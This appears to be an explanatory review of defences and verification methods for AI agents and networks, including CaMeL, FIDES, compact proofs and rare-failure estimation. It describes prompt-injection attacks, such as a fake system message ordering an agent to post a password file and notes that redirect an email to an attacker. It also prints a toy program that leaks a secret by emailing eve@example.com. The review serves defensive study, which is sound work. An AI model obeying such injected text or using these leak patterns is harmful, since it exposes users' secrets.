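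Random noise is also as likely to destroy the words that matter as any others. If a request is harmful because of two particular words, and the noise removes each with probability 0.25, both disappear from one copy in sixteen on average. A detector that judges the remaining text correctly can then call at most about 94% of the copies harmful, which limits the certified radius. Chen and colleagues suggest adding less noise to important words, or using facts about how the network behaves on several related inputs. Either approach would use knowledge that the black-box method leaves out, and nobody has yet found an efficient way to compute tight certificates from it.

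## CaMeL: proving the software around a language model

A certificate that covers only a few changed tokens does little to protect an assistant that reads whole emails from strangers. Another approach is to assume that an attacker can fool the model, and prove limits on what the surrounding software will then do. Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind and elsewhere took this approach in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), which introduced CaMeL, a system that protects agents. Agents are language models that can use tools, for example to read files, send email or move money.

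### Instructions hidden in data

An agent that obeys a prompt injection, an instruction hidden in material it reads, may take harmful actions. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) gives the example of an agent that sorts bug reports for a software project. One report ends with a fake system message telling the agent to open a file of passwords and post the contents as a public reply. According to Schmidt Sciences' *How to Stop an AI Agent From Being Fooled*, researchers deceived OpenAI's web-browsing agent Atlas within hours of its release, using text hidden in ordinary web pages.

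These attacks work because the model receives the user's request and the material it reads as a single sequence of tokens. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, compares this to SQL injection, in which a website pastes a visitor's text into a database command and the database runs part of it. Adversarial training makes models less likely to obey injected text, but doesn't guarantee that they won't. Willison considers a 99% detection rate a failing grade in security, because attackers will look for the other 1%.

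### Writing the plan before reading the data

CaMeL uses two language models and an interpreter, an ordinary program that runs code:

1. A privileged model sees the user's request and descriptions of the tools, but no untrusted data. It writes a program, in a restricted form of Python, that carries out the request.
2. The interpreter runs the program. When a step needs information from an email or file, a quarantined model reads the text and returns a value, such as an address. This model can't call tools.
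3. The interpreter stores the value and tags it with its origin and the people allowed to read it. Anything computed from the value inherits these tags.
4. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks a policy, a short function that uses the tags to allow or refuse the call.

Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and adds that the meeting notes contain his address and the document's name. The privileged model might write:

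```
notes = find_meeting_notes()
address = extract("Bob's address", notes)
title = extract("document Bob wants", notes)
document = fetch_file(title)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

An attacker called Eve has added a line to the notes telling the agent to delete the user's files and send the document to her. The deletion can't happen because the program has no step that deletes anything, and the privileged model finished writing it before the interpreter opened the notes. But Eve can still get the quarantined model to return her address as Bob's. The program then runs as written, with her address in its last line.

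Willison had proposed the two-model design in 2023 without noticing this flaw. CaMeL added the tags to fix it. If the policy lets the agent send a document only to people who already have permission to read it, the interpreter blocks the email to Eve. A stricter policy could require the address to come from a trusted source, but Bob's real address is in the same notes, so the agent would have to ask the user for approval. Eve could also change the document's name. If Bob is allowed to read the document she chooses, the first policy lets the agent send him the wrong file.

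### The guarantee and its assumptions

CaMeL guarantees two things. The first, which *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls control-flow integrity, is that every run follows a plan fixed by the user's request and other trusted information. Untrusted data can determine which of the plan's branches runs, but can't add a new one. The second is that no tool call goes ahead if the policy forbids it.

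The guarantee assumes that the user's request and the privileged model are trustworthy, that the tools work as described, that the tags and policies are correct, and that the interpreter enforces them correctly. It assumes nothing about the quarantined model, which can therefore be too large to verify.

A bad plan can make the first part useless. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) tested CaMeL on a task that told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a loop with a branch for every available tool, so whoever controlled the file could choose any of them. An attack succeeded when policy checks were turned off.

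Garby and colleagues also found that the interpreter sometimes loses track of its tags. For example, putting an untrusted value inside a longer string made it count as trusted. A subtler leak arises in a program like this, where the account balance is secret:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("eve@example.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL updates a variable's tag only when the program changes the variable. If the balance is high, the third line changes `tmp`, so the program skips the change to `rich`. `rich` therefore keeps its public tag, and the program sends the email, which reveals the secret. Eve can't insert this program herself, because the privileged model writes the code, but the example shows that the tracking isn't sound.

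CaMeL's designers did not prove a soundness theorem and called formalisation a "crucial direction" for later work. Garby and colleagues then designed a small programming language for agents and proved a version of the missing theorem in the proof checker Lean. Roughly, if two runs differ only in secret data, someone who sees only the public outputs can't tell them apart, except possibly by whether the program finishes. The same theorem, applied to trust instead of secrecy, limits what untrusted data can influence. It covers the interpreter that actually calls the model, though a program can explicitly declare untrusted data trustworthy.

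### Attacks stopped and tasks completed

The usual test is AgentDojo, which has 97 tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack (workplace chat) settings, and 629 test cases that pair a task with an injected attack. *SecureClaw* (2026) reports that none of the 629 attacks succeeded in a rerun of CaMeL's released code, adapted to the benchmark. But CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks without attacks. The paper's own system completed 59, though four attacks succeeded against it.

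CaMeL's original evaluation recorded two successful injections, according to Garby and colleagues. In one, the user had told the agent to make whatever payment a document specified, which CaMeL's designers consider outside their threat model. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and the benchmark wrongly counted the quotation as a successful attack.

Garby and colleagues reran the banking tasks to see what the policies contribute.

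| | Policies off | Policies on |
|---|---|---|
| Tasks completed with GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| Tasks completed with MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 37.5% |
| Successful attacks, both models | 5 of 622 | 0 of 588 |

Writing the plan first stops most attacks by itself. In 97 of the 144 banking combinations, the attack needs a tool call that would never appear in the plan, such as a payment when the user asked for a summary. In the other 47, the plan may already contain the call the attacker wants, so stopping the attack depends on a policy or on the quarantined model returning correct output despite the attack. The policies therefore add only a little protection, and enforcing them blocks nearly half of the tasks that would otherwise be completed.

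Without policies, CaMeL tends to reduce task completion less as the language model becomes more capable. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested a version for several cooperating agents with five language models and found that the reduction was modest for the strongest ones. CaMeL also uses more computation. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports that CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent on the median AgentDojo task with GPT-4o.

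Other defences can look better than CaMeL on a fixed test, where the attacks do not adapt to the defence. In one such test, *The Devil is in the Context* (2026) found that 17.5% of newly written attacks succeeded without a defence, 7.5% with PromptArmor and 2.5% with CaMeL. But agents completed 90% of tasks with PromptArmor and only 27.5% with CaMeL. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) tested a defence that checks actions outside the model, and fewer than 5% of adaptive attacks succeeded. The paper leaves the same test of CaMeL to future work.

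### Policies, approvals and false information

Someone has to write CaMeL's policies and keep them up to date. As with the ACAS Xu properties, a proof doesn't help if the policy is wrong. When a policy doesn't determine whether an action is safe, the system can ask the user, but users who are asked too often start approving everything. Willison points out that even the security researcher Troy Hunt fell for a phishing email while jet-lagged.

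Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, argue that the usual comparisons are unfair to systems like CaMeL. The undefended agent gets credit for actions that a real product would ask the user to approve, while the defended one gets no human help. They instead count how many approvals an agent needs. Their agent, Prudentia, is given the policies and takes them into account when planning. It can also ask the user to vouch for a piece of data once. If an email lists ten jobs, the user can approve the email instead of ten separate actions. On AgentDojo, Prudentia cut the number of approvals by a factor of up to 1.9 compared with FIDES, an earlier Microsoft system.

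False information is harder to deal with. An injected line can make the quarantined model summarise a bad report as a good one, and no policy on tool calls will detect it. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) adapt CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen, and show that false information can also steer an agent between branches of a legitimate plan. The plan has to anticipate what might appear, including cookie notices, so an attacker can disguise an advertisement as a cookie notice and get the agent to click it. Policies help little here, because the effect of a click depends on what is on the screen. On OSWorld, a test of everyday computer tasks, the adapted agents kept up to 57% of the performance of leading models.

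Reducing such errors means making the quarantined model itself harder to fool. Adversarial training could help, as could a mechanistic explanation of how models confuse instructions with data, but CaMeL's limits on tool calls require neither.

### Plans that depend on what the agent reads

If a user asks an agent to do today's tasks from a to-do list, the privileged model can't write the full plan without knowing what is on the list. In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) found that 43.8% of AgentDojo's banking tasks and 42.9% of its Slack tasks depend on data in this way, compared with 5% of office tasks and 10% of travel tasks.

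Their system, FIDES, plans one step at a time. It hides untrusted results in variables, as CaMeL does, but the planner can choose to open one. Everything the planner does afterwards counts as untrusted, and the policies block risky actions. The planner can often avoid opening a variable by having a quarantined model answer a yes-or-no question about its contents, such as whether an email asks for a meeting. An attacker may be able to flip the answer, but can't use it to pass an instruction to the planner because it is only one bit.

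FIDES also tracks who may read each piece of data. If R(x) is the set of people allowed to read x, then anything made from x and y has the readers

R(x, y) = R(x) ∩ R(y).

In an example from Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, Alex's agent reads one email shared between Alex and Priya and another shared between Alex and Marco. Only Alex has access to both, so the agent can't send Marco a reply based on both emails without approval. This rule also catches accidental leaks.

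The formal guarantee covers direct flows of data but not what an observer could infer from which tools the agent calls. Costa and colleagues chose this weaker property because blocking every indirect leak would make too many tasks impossible. They tested FIDES with GPT-4o and measured the share of tasks completed without attacks:

| Setting | Ordinary agent, no policies | Ordinary agent with policies | FIDES with policies |
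|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

The researchers counted 152 successful injections against the ordinary agent without policies and none against either system with policies. AgentDojo's automatic check recorded three against FIDES, but the researchers judged these to be permitted actions or scoring errors. A stronger model, o1, raised FIDES's score on travel tasks from 41% to 68%.

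### Several agents, smaller models and early checks

CaMeL's guarantee can fail when protected agents work together. In a test by Peters-Gill and colleagues, a user asked for a summary of job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack. A database agent returned the records along with an injected instruction, and a coordinating agent pasted the resulting summary into its message to a third agent. Although all three agents were running CaMeL, the third treated the whole message as a trusted request, so its privileged model added a step that emailed the applicants' details to the attacker. Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed this by sending instructions and untrusted data between agents through separate channels. On their multi-agent benchmark, 0.0% of attacks then succeeded, compared with 0.2% when each agent was protected separately and 12.9% with no protection.

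Small models often can't write the programs CaMeL needs. Nakayama (2026), in *CapLite*, found that the programs failed to run in up to 68% of attempts, depending on the model. CapLite allows an action that changes something only if the user's request states every detail that determines whom or what the action affects, and it doesn't ask the model to write its security rules. None of 13,935 attacks succeeded, and CapLite used 18% as many tokens as CaMeL. But CapLite would block the email to Bob, because his address is in the notes, not the request.

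*CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) checks the whole plan before it runs. If a security team requires approval before anyone disconnects a computer, the tool can reject a plan that has no approval step and send the reason to the privileged model, which then tries again. CaMeL would detect the problem only when the plan reached the disconnection step.

### Early deployment

Microsoft added FIDES to its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, as an experimental feature in May 2026. It also worked with GitHub on experimental support in the coding assistant GitHub Copilot CLI, where FIDES so far enforces policies only for selected GitHub tools. In the Agent Framework, developers have to label each source of data, and the system treats unlabelled data as trusted and public. An attacker who can write to an unlabelled source can therefore get past the policies even if the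 proof is correct. Microsoft has asked developers whether unlabelled data should count as untrusted instead.

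## Compact proofs: whether understanding a model makes it easier to verify

CaMeL provides its guarantee without examining the language model. Verifiers that do examine networks, such as those used on ACAS Xu, can run out of time as networks grow. Someone who knows how a network works might be able to skip most of the checking. Gross, Agrawal and colleagues (2024), in *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability*, tested this idea on networks small enough that they could also check every input and compare the results.

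### A network that picks the largest number

They trained 151 small transformers to read four whole numbers from 0 to 63 and output the largest. There are 64⁴ = 16,777,216 possible inputs. Running a network on all of them proves exactly how accurate it is (99.92% on average), but this takes about 2⁴⁷ arithmetic operations. With ten numbers instead of four, there would be about 10¹⁸ inputs.

Each network has 8,320 weights and a single attention head, a component that divides its attention among the numbers in the input and combines what it reads from each in proportion. The researchers studied the weights of one network and found that it works in two steps:

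1. It gives more attention to larger numbers. Each increase of 1 multiplies the attention by about 3.4.
2. It copies the numbers it attends to into the output, so the one with the most attention normally gets the highest score.

For the input 12, 31, 5, 30, the 31 gets about 77% of the attention and the 30 gets nearly all the rest. For the harder input 30, 30, 31, 30, the 31 gets only 53%. The order of the numbers hardly matters. Copying is unreliable for roughly the seven smallest numbers, but this affects the answer only when all four numbers are that small, which happens in about 0.01% of inputs. Measurements on the other 150 networks fitted the same explanation.

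### From sixteen million cases to a few thousand

The first shortcut relies only on how the network's parts fit together. Gross and colleagues proved that they needed to check only inputs with at most three different values: the largest, the last, and one other. For example, the network must be right on the input [50, 20, 35, 40] if it is right on all the simpler inputs made from the same values, such as [50, 20, 20, 40] and [50, 35, 35, 40].

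There are 64³ = 262,144 ways to choose three values. Because order hardly matters, the researchers could assume the worst order each time without weakening the guarantee much. They also computed the network's internal tables once and reused them. The resulting proof took about 2²⁵ operations, roughly four million times fewer than checking every input, and guaranteed an average accuracy of 95.31%. It left about 787,000 inputs unproved, although a typical network gets only about 13,000 wrong.

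The next shortcut uses the attention pattern. Numbers well below the largest get almost no attention, so a proof can treat them all as if they were the most harmful one. The proof then goes through 4,096 pairs of values instead of triples. This cut the computation by another factor of 16 but lowered the guaranteed accuracy to 70.2%.

Much of the loss comes from combining worst cases that can't occur together, as interval arithmetic does. Suppose one part of a network adds 3 to the correct answer's lead when the largest number is odd and 0 when it is even, and another part does the reverse. The lead is always 3, but adding the worst case for each part gives 0. Gross and colleagues reduced this problem by moving the average effect of one part into the other before taking worst cases, which gives 3 in this example. Without that step, they could guarantee only 34.9%.

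| Proof | Operations | Guaranteed accuracy | Numbers left unexplained |
|---|---|---|---|
| Check every input | 2⁴⁷ | 99.92% | 2³⁰ |
| Check inputs with at most three different values | 2²⁵ | 95.31% | 2¹⁴ |
| Treat small numbers together | 2²¹ | 70.2% | 2¹³ |
| Also reduce attention to one simple pattern | 2²² | 67.5% | 2¹² |
| Also simplify the path that bypasses attention | 2²¹ | 61.0% | 2¹³ |

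The last column estimates how many numbers someone would still need to describe the network's behaviour if the assumptions behind the proof were right. Without an explanation, they would need 64 output scores for each of 16.8 million inputs, or about a billion numbers. Across 102 proof strategies, shorter proofs tended to leave less unexplained but give looser bounds. The last two simplifications saved nothing in a network of this size. They would matter more in larger networks, but the researchers never found a much shorter way to handle the copying step.

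### How a better explanation tightens the bound

Some of the short proofs replace the full attention table with the single rule that larger numbers get more attention. This rule fits some networks better than others. On average, the main pattern in the table was about 620 times as strong as the next. For proofs of similar length, a better fit went with a tighter bound. In the type of proof with the clearest trend, the fitted line was

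share of true accuracy proved = 0.44 + 0.0002 × (strength of main pattern / strength of next).

If the ratio rises from 500 to 800, the predicted share rises from 54% to 60%. The ratio explained about 41% of the variation in the share between networks.

Compact proofs give researchers a way to grade explanations. *Evaluating Explanations* (2025) describes the method as a program that takes a model's weights and an explanation and computes a guaranteed lower bound on the model's performance. A tight bound that takes little computation should distinguish a good explanation from one that merely sounds right.

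The savings do not include the work of finding the explanation, which people did by hand. Testing is also a better way to learn a network's average accuracy. A test of one of these networks on 10,000 random inputs would normally give its accuracy to within about 0.06 percentage points, far closer than the 95.31% bound. However, an unlucky sample can make a test result misleading, and a proof avoids that risk.

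### Small errors that add up

An explanation of a network always leaves something out, and a proof based on that explanation has to assume that the omitted parts do as much damage as possible. Small errors in random directions mostly cancel, but in the worst case they add up, as an attacker's changes to pixels do. If 10,000 unexplained effects each shift the result by 0.001, the total shift is typically about 0.1 but 10 in the worst case, which could easily exceed the margin by which the network favours the correct answer.

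Gross and colleagues had this problem even with a one-layer model. They could safely simplify the finished attention table, which is the product of several smaller tables. But when they simplified the smaller tables first, the worst-case error was orders of magnitude larger than the real one, which made the bound useless. They suspect that there is often no short explanation of why such errors cancel. Errors also have more chances to build up in a network with many layers. One possible remedy is to estimate the typical effect of these errors instead of proving a worst-case bound.

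### How small the understood models are

The Alignment Research Center (ARC) uses a stricter standard of understanding, which is whether someone can calculate a model's accuracy from its weights at least as efficiently as by testing it. In January 2026, ARC published a set of tiny models trained on simple tasks, described in *AlgZoo*. The largest model that ARC's researchers believe they more or less fully understand has 32 weights.

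Their smallest example has 10 weights and finds the position of the second-largest of two numbers, x₀ and x₁. Where it can go wrong, its answer depends on the sign of

a₀x₀ − a₁x₁.

The model would be perfect if a₀ and a₁ were equal, but they differ by about one part in 2,048. This slightly tilts the boundary between its two answers. The model gets the inputs between the tilted boundary and the correct one wrong, and these make up about 1/(2π × 2,048) of all inputs, or one in 13,000. A few calculations therefore give an error rate that would take tens of thousands of tests to measure.

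ARC has not yet succeeded with a 432-weight model that does the same task with ten numbers. It worked out what 5 of the model's 16 internal units do, which is mostly to keep track of the largest number seen, but the rest are more densely connected. Errors in ARC's approximations also mattered more as the units became more complex. ARC would consider it a major breakthrough to calculate this model's accuracy as efficiently as sampling does. Gross and colleagues' networks are larger, but a partial explanation was enough for their proofs.

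### Estimating failures too rare to observe

Testing can easily measure a model's average accuracy, but the probability of a failure that occurs once in a hundred million inputs is hard to measure this way. Wu and Hilton (2024), in *Estimating the Probabilities of Rare Outputs in Language Models*, studied how to estimate such probabilities in language models with one, two and four layers. They counted it as a "failure" when the model gave a particular token the highest probability of coming next. They measured the true probabilities by running about four billion random inputs, and these lay between 10⁻⁹ and 10⁻⁵.

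Each estimator could use only 2¹⁶ = 65,536 runs of the model. For a failure with probability 10⁻⁷, ordinary sampling would have less than a 1% chance of producing even one case, so it would almost always give an estimate of zero. Wu and Hilton tried two kinds of alternative.

Importance sampling deliberately draws inputs that are likely to cause the failure, then corrects for having done so. If p(x) is the probability of an input in normal use and r(x) its probability in the search, then

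P(failure) = average over inputs drawn from r of [ F(x) × p(x)/r(x) ],

where F(x) is 1 if the model fails and 0 otherwise. If 10% of the inputs drawn cause a failure and each was a million times more likely in the search than in normal use, the estimate is 0.1 × 10⁻⁶ = 10⁻⁷. One version used gradients to choose each token separately, and another changed an input step by step.

Activation extrapolation uses a model's activations on ordinary inputs to estimate how often a failure would occur, even if none of those inputs causes it. The simpler version fits a bell curve to the gap between the target token's score and the highest score, then calculates how often the target would have the highest score. The other version splits each activation into a part that makes the target more likely and a remainder, then combines every such part with every remainder. This turns 65,536 real activations into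 about four billion artificial ones, but it assumes that the two parts vary independently, which is often untrue.

Both approaches beat ordinary sampling, and importance sampling did best. But the comparison first adjusted each method's estimates using the true probabilities, which would be unknown in practice. *Estimating Rare Events in Language Models with Proper Evaluation* (Parulekar and Liu, 2026) compared the methods without this adjustment. For the rarest failures, importance sampling often found no failing input and gave an estimate of zero, while recombining activations gave estimates that were too high.

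Their own method breaks a rare event into a chain of more common ones. If one activation in ten reaches the first level, and one in ten of those reaches the next, eight such steps give a probability of 10⁻⁸. The method was usually more accurate than recombination when overestimates and underestimates counted equally. When underestimates counted much more, recombination did better because it tended to overestimate, so a safety auditor might reasonably prefer it.

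None of these methods explains the model, and importance sampling has to find inputs that make the model fail. Wu and Hilton point out that finding them can be impossible, as with the RSA-2048 trigger. They give the example of a model that misbehaves only if SHA-256, a standard function that scrambles its input into 256 bits, outputs one particular value. Someone who could see this rule in the model could treat the scrambled bits as random and estimate the probability of misbehaviour at 2⁻²⁵⁶. Relaxed adversarial training needs estimates of this kind.

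### Calculating instead of sampling

The Alignment Research Center hopes to automate such reasoning. Its *Competing with sampling* gives the example of a catastrophe that requires three independent conditions, each with a one-in-a-million probability. Estimating each condition separately takes about three million samples in total, and multiplying the results gives 10⁻¹⁸. Direct sampling would take about 10¹⁸ samples. The gain depends on the conditions being independent. If they always occurred together, the true probability would be 10⁻⁶, a trillion times higher than the estimate.

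ARC conjectures that, given a suitable explanation of a network's structure, a calculation from the weights can always do at least as well as sampling for the same amount of computation. An algorithm would use this explanation, which might be as long as the network and just as unreadable to people.

Wu, Lecomte and colleagues (2026) showed in *Estimating the expected output of wide random MLPs more efficiently than sampling* that this works for simple networks with random weights. They describe the activations in each layer by their means, variances and covariances, and sometimes by finer details of their distribution. They then calculate how each layer changes this description, without running the network on any inputs.

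A single ReLU unit shows the advantage of calculating an average over estimating it by sampling. If the unit's input is normally distributed with mean 0 and standard deviation 1, its average output is 1/√(2π) ≈ 0.399. Sampling would take about 340,000 inputs to estimate that average with a typical error of 0.001. In a deep network the distributions are no longer exactly normal, so the calculation becomes approximate.

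In networks with four hidden layers of 256 units, the best versions were about 10 to 100 times as efficient as sampling. One version estimated the probabilities of rare events, around one in 570,000, with a relative error below 30%, using about as much computation as 5,695 samples. That many samples would have had about a 1% chance of including such an event. With eight hidden layers, however, the most detailed versions did worse than sampling.

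The larger problem is that trained networks have structure that random weights don't. The Alignment Research Center (ARC) has since organised a contest with AIcrowd, again on random networks, and the announcement describes the same task for trained networks as "remarkably hard". *A Mike's-Eye View of ARC's Research*, by an ARC staff member, describes a plan to watch a model during training, record each new structure as it forms, and use the record to estimate the probability of catastrophe. The model would then be trained to lower that estimate. The staff member acknowledges that ARC doesn't yet fully understand any non-trivial problem that involves using structure in this way.

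### Interpretability in use at the end of 2026

The largest developers have meanwhile turned to more immediate uses of interpretability. Lindsey (2026) explains in *Interpretability team priorities update* that Anthropic's team long aimed to understand networks' mechanisms completely, but found this difficult. The team now concentrates on work likely to help with safety within 6 to 18 months.

Part of the reason is that newer models can solve more problems without writing out their reasoning, so people who read only the written reasoning may miss more. The team also investigates incidents where it matters what information the model was using when it acted, including cyberattacks by AI systems on real people and attempts to hide forbidden actions.

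Tools that translate activations into text have made more progress. Anthropic trained Claude to translate its own activations this way, and the company now uses tools of this kind to monitor deployed models. Lindsey's team doesn't consider them reliable enough to be the main defence. A readable translation may be wrong, and it provides no bound on how often the model will fail. Like the linear probes in Anthropic's filters, these monitors can be useful long before anyone can explain the computations they monitor.

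Google DeepMind's team made a similar change a year earlier. *A Pragmatic Vision for Interpretability* (Nanda, Engels and colleagues, 2025) describes the team's move from ambitious reverse-engineering to problems where they can measure progress. In a talk about the decision, *Our Pivot To Pragmatic Interpretability*, Neel Nanda cited Anthropic's study of how Claude Sonnet 4.5 recognised tests. In that study, simple differences between activations gave useful results without a nearly complete account of the model.

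### Reasons to expect more, and reasons to expect little

Amodei argues that better interpretability could greatly help developers set bounds on a model's possible errors. The experiments give this some support. Knowing how a network's parts fit together cut the computation needed for a proof by a factor of four million, while lowering the accuracy it guaranteed by less than five percentage points. Calculations from the weights have also estimated the probability of rare events better than sampling. Much of the remaining work is finding explanations and writing programs that use them. AI may greatly reduce the effort this takes, as it did for the verifier Vibecheck. ARC also estimates that even if finding an explanation took as much computation as training the model, the total computation would only double. Its new executive director, in *returning to arc* (2026), calls the programme an ambitious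 bet and is excited about its chances.

One reason to expect little is that the difficulties already appear in very small models. Worst-case errors ruined some proofs about a one-layer network, and ARC still struggles to analyse a model with 432 weights, while Llama-3.1-8B has almost 20 million times as many. Cryptography suggests a deeper obstacle, since most cryptographers believe a program can be scrambled so thoroughly that no efficient method could learn more from its code than from its inputs and outputs. Ordinary training doesn't scramble a network deliberately, but ARC thinks a network's structure could be hidden in its finished weights in this way, which is partly why it thinks its methods will have to follow the training process.

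Even a good estimator would need a mathematical definition of catastrophe and a description of the inputs the model will receive, and ARC has spent little time on either. ARC's most concrete test for now is the public challenge to calculate the 432-weight model's accuracy as efficiently as sampling can measure it.
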